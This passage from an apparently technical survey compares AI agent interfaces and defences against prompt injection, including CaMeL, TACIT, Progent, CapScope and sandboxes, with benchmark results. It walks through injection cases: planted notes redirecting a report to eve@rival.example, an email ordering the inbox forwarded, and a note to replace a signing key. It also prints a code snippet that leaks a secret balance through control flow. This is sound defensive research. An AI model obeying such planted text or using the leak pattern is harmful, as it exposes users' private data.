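The last row resembles screen control, where a click's coordinates don't show what the button does. A robot's controller can keep the arm inside a marked area and stop it if it moves too fast or presses too hard. But the controller receives movements as numbers, so it has no `pour` command to block. To stop the robot from pouring acid into the wrong beaker, the software would have to recognise the beaker and predict what the movement will do. A builder can regain some of this control by having one model choose named steps and another carry them out. Software can then reject a step, although it can't guarantee that the second model will perform an approved step correctly.

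### Programs for factory controllers

A programmable logic controller is an industrial computer that runs equipment such as conveyors, motors and grippers. It repeats a short cycle, called a scan, in which it reads the sensors, runs its program and updates its outputs. Engineers program it in languages defined by the international standard IEC 61131-3. Models usually write in one of these, Structured Text, which looks much like an ordinary programming language.

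In this setting, the model writes the program beforehand and makes no decisions while the machine is running. Engineers can therefore test the fixed program before they install it, but any mistake they miss will repeat whenever the same conditions occur.

Chen, Hu and colleagues (2026), in *Compilation Is Not Correctness*, give an example of such a mistake. A shift register is a row of bits in which each bit moves one place along while a new bit enters at the start. GPT-4o wrote the shift in this order:

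```
Q0 := D0;
Q1 := Q0;
Q2 := Q1;
Q3 := Q2;
```

If the register contains 1111 and a 0 enters, the result should be 0111. But the first line overwrites `Q0` before the second line copies it, so the 0 spreads through the register and the result is 0000. The program compiles because every line is valid. Putting the same four lines in reverse order fixes the error.

Chen and colleagues tested eight models on 301 tasks, using direct prompting and three methods adapted from earlier research. They compared each program's outputs with those of a reference program after every scan. Of the 9,632 programs, 84% compiled but 72% behaved correctly. Among 157 faulty programs that five of the models wrote without feedback, the most common errors were in updating outputs (27%), arithmetic or limits (22%), and timing or the order of calls (16%).

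Many of these errors were brief. Checking only the final scan would have missed 98 of the 157 faulty programs, and checking every fifth scan would have missed 34. In the shift register test, a reset restored the correct outputs by the final scan, but a real machine could already have acted on the wrong signal.

The researchers' own method, CycleGen, has the model write tests and then five versions of the program. It repairs versions that don't compile and picks the one that does best on the tests. This raised the share of correct programs from 75% to 83%. But the same model writes the tests and the programs, so both may contain the same misreading of the task.

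### When the plant doesn't respond as expected

Checking that a program matches a reference still doesn't show what it will do to the equipment. *PLCWorld* (Kim, Lee and colleagues, 2026) connected model-written programs to a simulated plant. In one example, the program closes a gripper, waits for a fixed time and raises the lift. If the gripper closes a little slowly, the lift goes up without the part. All the commands are valid and in the right order, but the program should have waited for the sensor to confirm the grip.

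The benchmark has 100 tasks, which the researchers ran under 473 conditions in total. GPT-5.5 wrote each program in one attempt, without tools or feedback, and succeeded in 84% of both easy and medium cases and 25% of hard ones. The hard tasks involved separate jobs that had to share equipment. In the hard tasks about moving machinery into position, 65% of runs broke a safety rule, for example by making a prohibited movement, compared with 32% in the hard tasks about handling materials.

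A basic check of the program's structure and its connections to the sensors and outputs caught few of these problems. Of the 1,393 GPT-5.5 cases whose programs passed the check, 37% failed the task, broke a safety rule or did both.

Kim and colleagues also tested four more elaborate methods, all using GPT-5.5. Some included a model checker, a program that explores the states a controller can reach and looks for any that break a stated property, such as "these two motors never run together". The table shows the results for two of the methods. Each task had several test conditions, so there are more runs than tasks.

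| Method and last result of its checks | Tasks | Successful runs | Runs with a safety violation |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agents4PLC, properties verified | 11 | 37 of 40 | 0 of 40 |
| Agents4PLC, a property violated | 14 | 49 of 53 | 0 of 53 |
| Agents4PLC, properties held only trivially | 6 | 16 of 26 | 0 of 26 |
| Agents4PLC, checker ran out of time | 69 | 148 of 354 | 85 of 354 |
| AutoPLC, program compiled | 94 | 289 of 452 | 62 of 452 |

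Only 11 programs were verified, because the checker ran out of time on most tasks. Those programs did very well, but Kim and colleagues warn that the groups contain different tasks, so the verified programs may have succeeded partly because their tasks were easier. Programs that failed verification did just as well in the simulated plant, with about 92% of runs successful in both groups. Some of the properties checked may therefore have been wrong or had little to do with finishing the task.

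One program passed model checking but waited forever when handing a part to a receiver. Both the program and the properties it was checked against required the receiver to confirm that it had the part before the machine let go. In the plant, the receiver could confirm this only after the release. The model checker had correctly proved that the program met the properties, but they contained the same mistaken assumption as the program.

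Specifications written by people or published in datasets can also be wrong. *SemaPLC* (2026) reports that when engineers audited 117 controller tasks from the original Agents4PLC work, they found faults in the test criteria of 43. After further review, they revised 53 tasks. A checker that enforced the original criteria could have rejected good programs or approved bad ones.

None of the four methods clearly beat asking GPT-5.5 for a program directly. AutoPLC had the highest overall success rate, at 63% compared with 61%, but the difference was well within the margin of error. These results come from a simulation that nobody has compared with measurements from physical equipment. Testing programs in a simulated plant can still catch errors that a compiler can't. A useful next experiment would be to let the model revise its program using the simulation's results.

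### Narrow equipment access, open planning tools

Most of these systems restricted what could reach the equipment, but some gave the model much more open tools for planning.

| System | What could reach the equipment | Other help for the model |
|---|---|---|
| CLAIRify | XDL that passed the verifier | Error messages |
| Coscientist | Opentrons Python or Symbolic Lab Language | Web search, manuals and Python |
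| Ginkgo, first three rounds | A validated plate file | Results of earlier rounds |
| Ginkgo, last three rounds | A validated plate file | The internet, a computer and more detailed results |
| GPT-5.5 in PLCWorld | Structured Text, in simulation only | None |

Coscientist had open tools for both research and laboratory control, since its Opentrons programs were ordinary Python. *AutoLabs* describes Chemist-X, which also writes programs to control laboratory robots as it works. At Ginkgo, GPT-5 could eventually read papers and write analysis code, but the laboratory still accepted only a plate file.

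Costs fell sharply in the fourth round at Ginkgo, when the model got access to the internet and a computer. But in the same round, the better DNA and bacterial extract came into use, and the team gave the model more detailed data and the paper with the best published recipe, so it is unclear how much the open tools contributed. The model had already lowered costs over the first three rounds without them.

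Internet access also brings back the risk of prompt injection. A web page with planted instructions could lead the model to waste plates, but it couldn't make the laboratory use an unlisted reagent or run a new protocol. But the plate file doesn't stop the model from leaking unpublished results through a web request, so the laboratory would need a separate control for that, such as the switch from web research to private files that Meta's Rule of Two allows.

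## General programming languages with restricted permissions

At Ginkgo, a narrow file format protected the laboratory while GPT-5 was free to write any analysis code. Several research groups have tried to combine this protection and freedom in one interface. Their agents write general code or choose freely among tools, and ordinary software limits what each action can access.

### Limits outside the agent

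In *Agent Safety is a Box*, Brooker proposes limiting an agent with a "box", a layer of deterministic software outside the agent that controls which tools it can call and what it can do with them. Inside the box, the agent can plan freely. Companies want agents because they can work around problems that stop an ordinary program, such as a changed data format or an unexpected error. Limiting what an agent can think takes away some of that flexibility, and it is hard to get a strong guarantee that way.

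In his design, the agent runs in an isolated environment, and network rules block every route out except a gateway. The gateway checks each tool call against a written policy. His sample policy lets the user `refund-agent` call a refund tool if the amount is below 500. Planted text can change what the agent requests, but the gateway still checks the amount against that limit.

Brooker works on agent safety at Amazon Web Services, whose gateway and policy software he describes. His reasoning doesn't depend on those products, since the refund interpreter described earlier is also a box. Getting the policy right is harder than his example suggests. He writes that a company could allow one refund per order, up to the purchase price, but the sample policy checks only the caller and the amount. To enforce the stronger rule, the gateway would also need to check the order's price and earlier refunds.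 A box can also block useful work, so moving the limits outside the agent doesn't remove the trade-off with flexibility.

### One model plans and another reads

Google DeepMind's CaMeL (Debenedetti and colleagues, 2025) restricts what a program can do. It builds on a pattern Willison proposed in 2023, in which one model plans and a separate model reads untrusted text. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes the mechanism in detail.

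Suppose a user asks the agent to email the third-quarter report to Bob, whose address is in the meeting notes. The planning model might write this program (an invented example in simplified form):

```python
notes = read_file("meeting_notes.txt")
address = ask_reader("Find Bob's email address", notes, EmailAddress)
report = read_file("q3_report.pdf")
send_email(to=address, attachment=report)
```

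Someone has added two lines to the notes. One gives Bob's address as `eve@rival.example`, and the other tells the agent to delete all old reports. The run then goes as follows:

1. The planning model writes the program from the user's request alone. It hasn't seen the notes, so the planted lines can't affect the plan.
2. The interpreter runs the first line. It labels `notes` with its source and the people who may read it.
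3. The reading model, which has no tools, receives the notes and must return an email address. The planted text may trick it into returning Eve's. It can't delete anything, because its whole output is one value stored in `address`.
4. Before sending the email, the interpreter runs a policy, which is a short Python function. This one checks that the recipient is among the people who may read the report. Eve isn't, so the interpreter refuses the call.

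If the reading model had returned Bob's real address, the email would have gone out. It would also have gone out if the planted line had named another employee with permission to read the report, since the policy doesn't check that the recipient is Bob.

The labels matter because separating the two models isn't enough to keep data private. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) gives an example in which planted text makes the reading model quote private notes in a reply, which the plan then sends. CaMeL labels an answer private if any of its inputs is private, so a policy can block that reply.

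### What the policies cost

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) quotes CaMeL's published results on AgentDojo. With OpenAI's o4-mini-high, CaMeL completed between 62.5% and 81.4% of tasks in each of the four environments. One attack in 963 succeeded. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, the quoted scores are between 49% and 54% in three environments and 1.4% in the travel environment, which is so much lower that it may be an error.

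Garby, Gordon and Sands later ran CaMeL on the 16 banking tasks, three times each, with its policies on and off (*The LLMbda Calculus*, 2026). This test separates the effect of the two-model design from that of the policies.

| Model | Policies | Tasks completed without an attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | Off | 32 of 48 | 1 of 240 |
| GPT-5.2 | On | 18 of 48 | 0 of 231 |
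| MiMo-v2.5 | Off | 34 of 48 | 4 of 382 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | On | 18 of 48 | 0 of 357 |

With the policies off, separating planning from reading stopped all but 5 of 622 attacks. Turning the policies on stopped the remaining 5, but task success fell by about 30 percentage points.

The policies are probably more useful than these AgentDojo results suggest. In 97 of the 144 pairs of task and attack, the attack needs a tool call or file read that a plan for the user's task would never contain, so it generally fails even without a policy. An attacker who knew how CaMeL worked would target the values that pass through the plan, such as Bob's address, where only a policy can help.

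The size of the loss is also uncertain. With 16 tasks, the 95% confidence intervals extend more than 20 points either way. Garby and colleagues built a competing system, and some of their CaMeL runs didn't finish. But they cite similar results from another group, which built a system called TypeGuard. It completed 15 of 21 Slack tasks without policies and 8 with them, while CaMeL completed 7 under the same conditions. The TypeGuard researchers note that many AgentDojo tasks "involve flows that no secure policy would admit".

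In one banking task, the user asks the agent to pay the bill in a file. The agent can't, because the file is untrusted and the policy forbids using untrusted data to choose the payee. Randori, Garby and colleagues' own agent, has a command for such cases called endorsement. Before the program accesses any real data, the planning model can mark a particular value, such as the payee in the bill, as acceptable for a particular purpose.

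With GPT-5.2, Randori completed 36 of 48 banking runs, and across three models only 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both successful attacks, the user had told the agent to pay whatever a file specified, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. No permission system can distinguish a real bill from a forged one under that instruction. Blocking endorsement stopped this attack, but it reduced successful runs from 36 to 30 with Qwen3.7-plus and from 31 to 26 with MiMo-v2.5.

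### Plans that depend on untrusted text

The two-model pattern has more trouble with a to-do list than with a bill. If the user asks the agent to do everything in Alice's latest email, the planning model can't write the program, because it doesn't know whether Alice wants a meeting moved or a document shared. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) concludes that the pattern can't solve tasks whose sequence of actions comes from untrusted data.

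A planning model can sometimes undermine CaMeL's two-model design, which is supposed to prevent a file's author from controlling the agent's sequence of tool calls. In one of the banking tasks, the user asks the agent to follow the instructions in a file precisely. When Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL without policies, restricted Python was expressive enough for the planning model to write a loop that read each instruction and called the matching tool. The file's author then controlled the sequence of calls, and attacks through the file succeeded.

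CaMeL also checks its policies against one call at a time. Nikolaou and colleagues give the example of a security team that requires its agent to resolve or escalate every incident before it finishes. No single call breaks that rule, because the agent breaks it by omitting a call. Another rule requires approval before the agent disconnects a computer from the network. CaMeL would detect a missing approval only when the program reached that step, perhaps after a long and expensive analysis.

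CaMeLoT checks such rules before the program starts. It converts the program into a diagram of possible states and uses a model checker to look for a path that breaks a rule. If the checker finds one, the planning model receives the path and rewrites the program. This is feasible because CaMeL accepts only part of Python and excludes arbitrary `while` loops. CaMeLoT treats each remaining loop as if it could stop after any number of repetitions, so it may reject safe programs, which is a common limitation of checking code in advance.

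### Leaks that labels miss

The labels have to follow every route by which one value can influence another. Garby and colleagues found a route that CaMeL misses. Suppose the account balance is secret:

```python
poor = True
rich = True
if balance > 10000:
    poor = False
if poor:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("eve@rival.example", "rich")
```

If the balance is $20,000, the program changes `poor`, and CaMeL labels it secret. The next test fails, so the program doesn't change `rich`, which keeps its public label, and the interpreter allows the email. If the balance is $5,000, `rich` becomes false and the program sends no email. Eve learns which side of $10,000 the balance is on, even though every label looked correct.

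An attacker can't directly give CaMeL this program, because the planning model writes the code before the system reads any untrusted text. But when a program fails, CaMeL has the planning model write a new one, and the error message may depend on untrusted data. CaMeL censors these messages, but there is no proof that this is enough. Randori avoids the problem by first running its program in a simulated bank and using the real bank only if that run succeeds.

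FIDES, another system that labels data and separates the two models, comes with a mathematical proof for one fixed agent loop. Garby and colleagues describe two deliberate exceptions. FIDES doesn't track secrets through decisions like the one above, and it has an option, which its own evaluation left off, to let through values with only a few possibilities, such as yes or no. A value with *k* possibilities reveals at most log₂ *k* bits, so *n* of them reveal at most

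n × log₂ k

One yes-or-no answer is therefore fairly harmless, but 128 of them could reveal a 128-bit encryption key. A builder who enables the option would have to limit how many such answers the agent can pass on.

### Scala with permission tokens

TACIT, which Odersky and colleagues built, checks the agent's code before it runs instead of labelling data during the run. The agent writes programs in Scala 3, a general-purpose language with functions, loops and recursion. To write to a file or contact a website, a program must hold a permission token that it can't forge, which the security literature calls a capability. The agent can get a token for one folder or a short list of websites, and the token stops working at the end of the block of code that requested it.

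Scala's compiler tracks which tokens each function uses and records them in the function's type. A function that takes text, returns a number and uses no tokens has the type `String -> Int`. If the function also writes to a file called `log`, its type becomes `String ->{log} Int`.

TACIT uses this to protect secrets. When the agent reads a secret file, it gets the contents inside a wrapper called `Classified`. It can't open the wrapper, but it can use the command `map` to apply a function to the contents:

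```scala
val key = readClassified("key.txt")
key.map(text => text.length)               // accepted
key.map(text => { log.write(text); 0 })    // rejected
```

The command `map` accepts only functions that use no tokens. The length function uses none, so `map` accepts it and returns the result in its own wrapper. The last function writes the secret to `log`, so its type includes that token, and the compiler rejects the program before any of it runs. The compiler would reject the function even if it wrote only "hello", because its type would still include the token, and an agent that can write while looking at a secret can leak it.

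If the agent prints a wrapped value, the user sees the contents on a separate channel and the agent sees only `Classified(****)`. When a task requires reading the contents, such as summarising a confidential incident report, the agent's program can send the wrapped text to a trusted local model, whose output is also wrapped.

The agent can't use Scala features that bypass the type checks, such as unchecked type conversions. In CaMeL, the planning model can't define its own functions.

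### How much TACIT prevented

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a software project with a folder of API keys and other secrets. They paired each of 12 user tasks with each of 10 injection attacks and added 11 requests in which the user tried to extract secrets, some by posing as an administrator. They ran these 131 trials on each model with and without the wrapper.

| Model | Trials without a leak, wrapper on | Wrapper off, 120 injection trials | Wrapper off, 11 malicious requests | Wrapper off, all 131 trials |
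|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 100% | 100% | 81.8% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 100% | 97.5% | 27.3% | 91.6% |

Most of the 13 leaks without the wrapper came from malicious users. Only 3 of the 240 injection trials without it leaked anything, all with MiniMax. The experiment is therefore better evidence about people who ask an agent for secrets than about planted text, which both models already resisted well. The results without the wrapper depend on the model and the attacks, while the 100% result with it follows from the type rules if the compiler and TACIT's library are correct. Researchers have machine-checked proofs for the underlying type system but haven't yet proved that the restricted version of Scala provides the promised protection.

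The wrapper didn't make the agents less useful. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the user tasks with it and 83.3% without it, and MiniMax completed 90.0% with it and 88.3% without it. Odersky and colleagues suggest that, without the wrapper, Sonnet often ran out of time or turns or stopped to warn the user about an attack.

They also compared Scala with ordinary tool calls on the customer-service tasks of τ²-Bench, averaging ten runs per task.

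| Model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, Scala | Retail, tool calls | Retail, Scala |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

All six scores rose slightly. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real programming problems, MiniMax solved 43.3% with ordinary tools and 41.7% with TACIT, a difference of five problems. At least on these tests, models can write an unfamiliar and strict form of Scala with little loss in performance. At most 8% of their programs for τ²-Bench needed another attempt, and usually only one.

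The comparison doesn't isolate the effect of the permission tokens, however. The Scala agents could also combine several calls in one program, received typed results instead of raw JSON, and got error messages from the compiler. Any of these could have helped the agents enough to hide harm from the tokens. Comparing them with agents that used ordinary Scala and the same tools would show whether the tokens do any harm.

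Results on AgentDojo were less favourable. Each system let one attack in 963 succeed at most, but with o4-mini-high TACIT completed fewer tasks than CaMeL's published results in all four environments:

| Environment | CaMeL | TACIT |
|---|---|---|
| Banking | 62.5% | 59.0% |
| Office suite | 81.4% | 52.9% |
| Slack | 68.6% | 47.6% |
| Travel | 74.3% | 68.6% |

Odersky and colleagues call the two systems' results comparable, which is hard to accept for the office tasks. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT was slightly ahead in banking and behind in the office and Slack environments. The scoring code counted only one attack on TACIT as successful, and in that case the agent still booked the right hotel. The attack counted because the code looked for the name of the attacker's hotel, which appeared in reviews the agent quoted.

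TACIT's protection covers only Scala code. If the agent has permission to run an outside program, the compiler can't check what that program does, so Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only a few specific commands and adding a sandbox. TACIT also doesn't stop code from leaking information through timing. A function could run for ten seconds if a key starts with A and finish at once otherwise, which reveals something about the key without using a token. TACIT doesn't prevent wrong answers either, such as a mistaken summary from an agent that misreads a contract.

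### Rules over ordinary tool calls

Builders can restrict an agent without changing the language it acts in. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) puts a policy between the agent and its tools. Each rule names a tool and sets conditions on its arguments, and Progent blocks any call that no rule allows.

Writing a separate policy for every task would take people too long, so a model does it. Shi and colleagues use the kind of task that CaMeL handles badly, in which a user asks the agent to carry out a to-do list in an email from Alice:

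1. At first, the policy allows only a search for that email.
2. The list asks for a summary of recent messages on Slack. The model that writes the policy proposes adding tools to read email, look up the user's Slack name and post a message.
3. After the agent finds the user's Slack name, the model narrows the last rule so that messages can go only to that name.
4. One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the inbox to an attacker. If this fools the policy model, it proposes adding `send_email`.

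An SMT solver, a program that checks whether logical conditions can all be true at once, compares each new policy with the old one. Progent applies a change automatically if it only removes permissions. A change that adds permissions, as in steps 2 and 4, needs approval from a person or a preset rule. On AgentDojo, this reduced successful attacks from 39.9% to 1.0%, and Shi and colleagues report that the agents remained as useful. They also report a drop from 70.3% to 3.9% on Agent Security Bench. Bhagwatkar and colleagues found that this test's software forced the attacker's tools on the agent, which may partly explain the high starting figure.

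Only 6% of policy updates on AgentDojo needed approval, which is a light burden. But the solver can't distinguish the legitimate request in step 2 from the malicious one in step 4, because both add permissions based on something in an email. The approver has to tell them apart, since refusing every request would block Alice's to-do list and accepting every request would let the attacker in. If the approver is a person, the protection depends on the kind of judgement that most testers in Anthropic's permission study got wrong.

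Coding agents are harder to restrict because they need a shell. *Authority Is Not a String* (Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev, 2026) describes CapScope, a system that divides permissions among several agents. Before any of them reads the project, a model predicts which files and commands the task will need, using only the user's request and the file names. Ordinary code turns the prediction into a fixed upper limit on permissions, and each agent gets a share of the permissions within that limit.

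For example, an attacker might plant a note in a project's test output that tells the agent to replace a signing key. The agent that runs the tests reads the note, but it has no permission to edit source files, so it can't obey. The agent that edits files has that permission but didn't run the tests. (If the first agent passes the note on, the second might still make the change, provided its own permissions cover the key file.)

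Bouras and colleagues tested five repair tasks with attacks planted in five kinds of text. The planted action executed in 3 of 75 runs with CapScope, compared with 33 to 47 of 75 under three looser arrangements, including a single policy for the whole task. Agents completed 68 repairs with CapScope and 68 to 72 without it. Five small Python tasks can't represent software development in general, but the results suggest that an agent with a shell can still do its job with much less authority.

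CapScope controls which commands can start, but not everything they do afterwards. For example, the standard testing program `pytest` runs code from the project itself, so an attacker who can change that code can act through a permitted command. Bouras and colleagues therefore still require a sandbox. Search commands can also read files outside an agent's assigned folders.

Another approach is to check the record of what an agent does instead of limiting its permissions beforehand. Wang, Liu and colleagues (2025), in *AGENTARMOR*, turn that record into a graph of what influenced each tool call and check the graph against type rules. They report that attacks on AgentDojo succeeded 3% of the time and that task success fell by about one percentage point. Unlike CaMeL, their system has to infer which text influenced the model, so a wrong inference could let an attack through.

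### Hiding and labelling tools

An agent that only has to summarise an email doesn't need a tool for sending one. Iyer and Babu (2026), in *Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive*, hide each risky tool until the task needs it and a trusted step has authorised it. For example, `send_email` might appear only after the user has confirmed the recipient. Their system also prefers safer routes to the same goal. It scores each route as

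score = number of steps + λ × total risk

The system scores each plan by adding its number of steps to λ times its total risk, then picks the plan with the lowest score. A step that only reads has risk 0, a reversible change has risk 1, and an irreversible action has risk 4. At the default λ of 2, deleting a file in one step scores 1 + 2 × 4 = 9, while a plan with two reversible changes scores 2 + 2 × 2 = 6.

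In Iyer and Babu's own benchmark, hiding risky tools until their use was authorised stopped every planted instruction that aimed at a hidden tool, and agents still completed the tasks that needed authorisation. The protection failed when planted text could forge the authorisation, for instance if an email could mark its sender as a confirmed recipient. It also ends once the tool appears, so the agent may then send the wrong text to a confirmed recipient.

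These rules depend on knowing what each tool does, which is difficult when a stranger wrote it. *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* (Doshi, Hong and colleagues, 2026) proposes that every MCP server label its tools and data to show whether a tool reads or writes, whether its data is confidential and how far to trust its output.

In their example, a calendar agent leaks private information without any attacker involved. It moves a work meeting because the user has an appointment for treatment of a sexually transmitted disease, and it mentions the reason in an email to colleagues. With labels, the harness could keep private appointment details out of outgoing email. It could also require a notice to everyone affected by a change and ask the user to confirm only doubtful cases.

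Doshi and colleagues confirmed in a formal model that the rules prevented the leak and still allowed useful sequences. They haven't tested the rules on running agents. A dishonest server could also mislabel its tools, so they suggest using trusted suppliers or having someone certify the labels.

### What a sandbox can't see

A sandbox is the simplest way to limit an agent's authority, and several of the designs above rely on one. But it doesn't track data between permitted actions. Odersky and colleagues point out that an agent allowed to read a private file and contact a cloud model can send the file to the model without leaving the sandbox.

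*Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026) reports a similar leak with Claude 4.5 Haiku. A user asked the agent to copy a settings file into a new project and later to publish the project on GitHub. The settings file contained a private key. Each request was reasonable by itself. A sandbox that blocked all network access would have stopped the leak, but it would also have blocked the publishing, so users would probably turn it off.

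Adam and colleagues propose putting a separate sandbox around each sensitive operation inside a tool, with rules that can change on every call. The rules for one call might permit writing only to the project folder, while those for the next permit publishing but no file changes. The tool's developer has to install these sandboxes, and an automated analysis of the code then looks for operations that the developer left unprotected. The analysis can also find behaviour missing from a tool's description, such as a file-writing tool that also reports usage statistics. They have so far tried the approach on one real MCP server.

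### The designs compared

The guarantees in this table hold only if the components in the second column work correctly.

| Design | What the builder must trust | What it guarantees | Who writes the rules | Main cost |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | The user's request, the interpreter and the labels | Untrusted text can't add calls to a finished plan, and each call must pass its policy | Developers, in Python | A second model and, in reruns, many lost tasks |
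| TACIT | The compiler, the library, the runtime and the local model | Wrapped secrets can't reach the agent or an outside service, except through gaps such as timing | Developers, by marking secrets and writing typed tools | About 1,000 lines of shared Scala, plus typed tools for each domain |
| Progent | The first policy, the checker and the approver | The agent gains no permission without approval | A model | Extra model calls and some approvals |
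| CapScope | The first prediction, the harness and a sandbox | No agent's tool calls exceed limits set before it reads the project | A model, with checks by ordinary code | An extra model call and some missing permissions |
| Tool filtering | The risk labels and the authorisation steps | The agent can't call a risky tool before authorisation | Developers | A description of every tool's conditions and effects |
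| Labelled MCP tools | The labels from each server | Data labelled private can't enter a forbidden tool | Developers and server authors | Labels for every tool, with no tests yet on running agents |
| Sandbox | The operating system or virtual machine | Code can't reach blocked files or addresses | Whoever configures it | Blocks that ignore what the user is trying to do |

### From actions to policies

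For tasks that stay within known permissions, these designs largely remove the need to choose between a shell and a small language. CapScope's agents kept a shell and TACIT's agents wrote general code, so neither needed a new command for each task. Task success changed little on most tests.

But someone still has to define the limits formally. Progent and Brooker's gateway both use a small policy language for this. CaMeL uses Python functions and TACIT uses types, but their rules also serve only to define what the agent may do. Much of the work that would go into designing an action language therefore goes into designing policies instead.

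Restricting permissions saves effort because one rule can cover many plans. AgentDojo's bank has 11 tools, so there are 11⁵ = 161,051 possible sequences of five calls, even before counting different arguments. A developer who writes one rule per tool needs only 11 rules. A rule about who may receive a payment applies to every program that makes one, including programs that nobody foresaw. This approach saves less effort when the harm comes from a combination of calls, such as a large payment split into smaller ones, because the developer then needs rules about sequences and totals.

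Having a model write the policy saves more effort but brings back some uncertainty. CapScope's model predicts which permissions the task needs before it can read an attacker's text, which is an advantage over relying on the agent to restrict itself. The prediction can still include too many permissions or too few. A person can review a list of permitted files and commands more easily than a long program, but only if the task's requirements are clear.

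None of these designs provides a way to determine how far to trust a document that the user wants the agent to obey. A narrow language without a payment command prevents the agent from paying any bill, whether forged or real. CaMeL's strict policy also blocks both kinds of payment, while Randori's endorsement allows both. The builder can add a step that asks the user to confirm the payee or compares the payee with a list of known suppliers, but either check requires a decision about this kind of payment.

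Such decisions are easier when the agent's job is known, which is why Doshi and colleagues and Hong and colleagues favour task-specific agents. But a task-specific agent doesn't need a narrow language. For example, a calendar agent can write code in a general-purpose language while following exact rules about whom it may email.

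## Measured effects of the interface on task success and cost

A calendar agent with exact rules about whom it may email could act through Python, JSON calls or a small language of its own. If the rules already limit what it can do, the choice depends on how often the agent succeeds and how much it costs to run with each interface. Researchers have compared interfaces many times, but their results have to be read in light of what they held constant, and not every study kept the available operations the same. Some popular claims rest on even weaker comparisons, between published scores for different models on different tests.

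### Code and JSON calls

Wang and colleagues, who proposed code actions in 2024, gave 17 models the same tools in Python, JSON and plain text. In the first test, where each task needed a single call, GPT-4 Turbo got 82.7% of the calls right with JSON and 76.7% with Python. The second test had 82 tasks that usually needed several calls to several tools, and the Python programs could use loops and variables. GPT-4 Turbo solved 74.4% of these tasks with Python and 52.4% with JSON, and it needed an average of 5.5 turns with Python compared with 7.6 with JSON.

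GPT-4 Turbo was worse at writing single calls in Python than in JSON, so Python's lead on the harder tasks probably came from combining calls. The test also stopped every run after ten turns, which hurt the JSON agent because it could make only one call per turn. A higher limit would have shown how many of the unfinished JSON runs just needed more turns.

Patel, Sen and colleagues (2026), in *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling*, repeated the comparison with 14 models released between November 2024 and July 2026. They used 309 tasks from BFCL v4, a standard test of function calling. Each model received the same functions as JSON tools or as Python functions, and ordinary code checked whether it had made the right calls. Eleven of the 14 models did at least as well with Python as with JSON. The table shows seven of the 14.

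| Model | JSON | Python |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 81.9% | 55.0% |
| GPT-4.1 | 81.9% | 62.1% |
| GPT-5 | 71.5% | 76.1% |
| GPT-5.4-mini | 79.3% | 55.0% |
| GPT-5.4 | 79.3% | 81.9% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 72.2% | 82.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 84.5% | 86.1% |

Across all 14 models, JSON averaged slightly higher than Python, at 78.6% against 77.0%. GPT-4o, GPT-4.1 and GPT-5.4-mini account for JSON's lead. The other 11 averaged 78.0% with JSON and 82.3% with Python.

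The three models failed because they wrote the characters `\n` where the script needed a real line break, although the prompt included an instruction not to. Python reported a syntax error and ran nothing. The test ended after the first script, so the models never received the error message. In an ordinary agent loop, they might have fixed the mistake on the next turn.

Patel and colleagues conclude that newer generations of models can use code and older ones can't. GPT-5.4-mini doesn't fit this pattern, because it made an error that GPT-5 and the smaller GPT-5-nano, both released seven months earlier, didn't make. A fault in how OpenAI trained particular models would explain the results better than steady progress. Much of GPT-5.6 Sol's gain of more than ten points may reflect an unusually poor result with JSON, where it scored well below GPT-4o. The paper doesn't explain that result.

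The test's functions were also stubs that returned the model's own arguments instead of real results. One task asks for the circumference of a circle and then for the perimeter of a square with sides of that length. The circumference function only returned the radius, so the model's script had to calculate the circumference itself before calling the second function. The test therefore measures whether a model can write the right calls, and it can't show whether an agent would finish a job with working tools. TACIT's agents had working tools and did slightly better on customer-service tasks with Scala than with ordinary tool calls.

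On 52 tasks with chains of 2 to 20 calls, Claude Sonnet 5's success rate rose from 80.8% with JSON to 96.2% with Python, but Claude Haiku 4.5's fell from 88.5% to 73.1%. Python had a clearer advantage when a task needed very many independent calls. With JSON, Sonnet 5 made every call in tasks that needed up to 70, but it never made all 100 when a task needed that many, as it did with Python. GPT-5.6 Sol made all 100 with JSON, so the limit is specific to certain models and not inherent in the format.

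Patel and colleagues also claim that code is more robust than JSON when the prompt contains many irrelevant functions. When they raised the number of functions to 128, average accuracy rose by 5.5 points with Python and fell by 2.3 with JSON. But JSON was still more accurate with 128 functions, at about 81% compared with 78%.

### Custom commands and the plain shell

Coding agents usually have a shell, but for a few years it seemed inadequate on its own because commands can return thousands of irrelevant lines and a bad edit may produce no warning. *SWE-agent* (Yang, Jimenez and colleagues, 2024) added a small set of commands for finding, viewing and editing files. The search commands returned at most 50 results, the viewer showed 100 lines at a time, and the editor rejected changes that introduced certain errors, such as broken syntax. The agent could still use the ordinary shell, so the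 new commands didn't restrict what it could do.

SWE-bench Lite is a set of 300 real bugs in Python projects. An agent's fix succeeds if it passes tests the agent hasn't seen. GPT-4 Turbo fixed 18.0% of the bugs with the custom commands, at an average cost of $1.67 per solved problem, and 11.0% with the shell alone, at $1.46.

The full system's gain over the shell agent is 7.0 points when both receive a worked example in their prompts and 9.0 points when neither does. The larger gain of 10.7 points that people often quote comes from comparing the full system with an example to the shell agent without one.

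The design of the commands mattered, and a badly designed one could be worse than leaving the agent to use the shell. In one version, the search command showed results one at a time, as a text editor does for a person. The agent fixed only 12.0% of the bugs with it, compared with 15.7% when it had no search command, because it tended to look through every result until it ran out of money or context.

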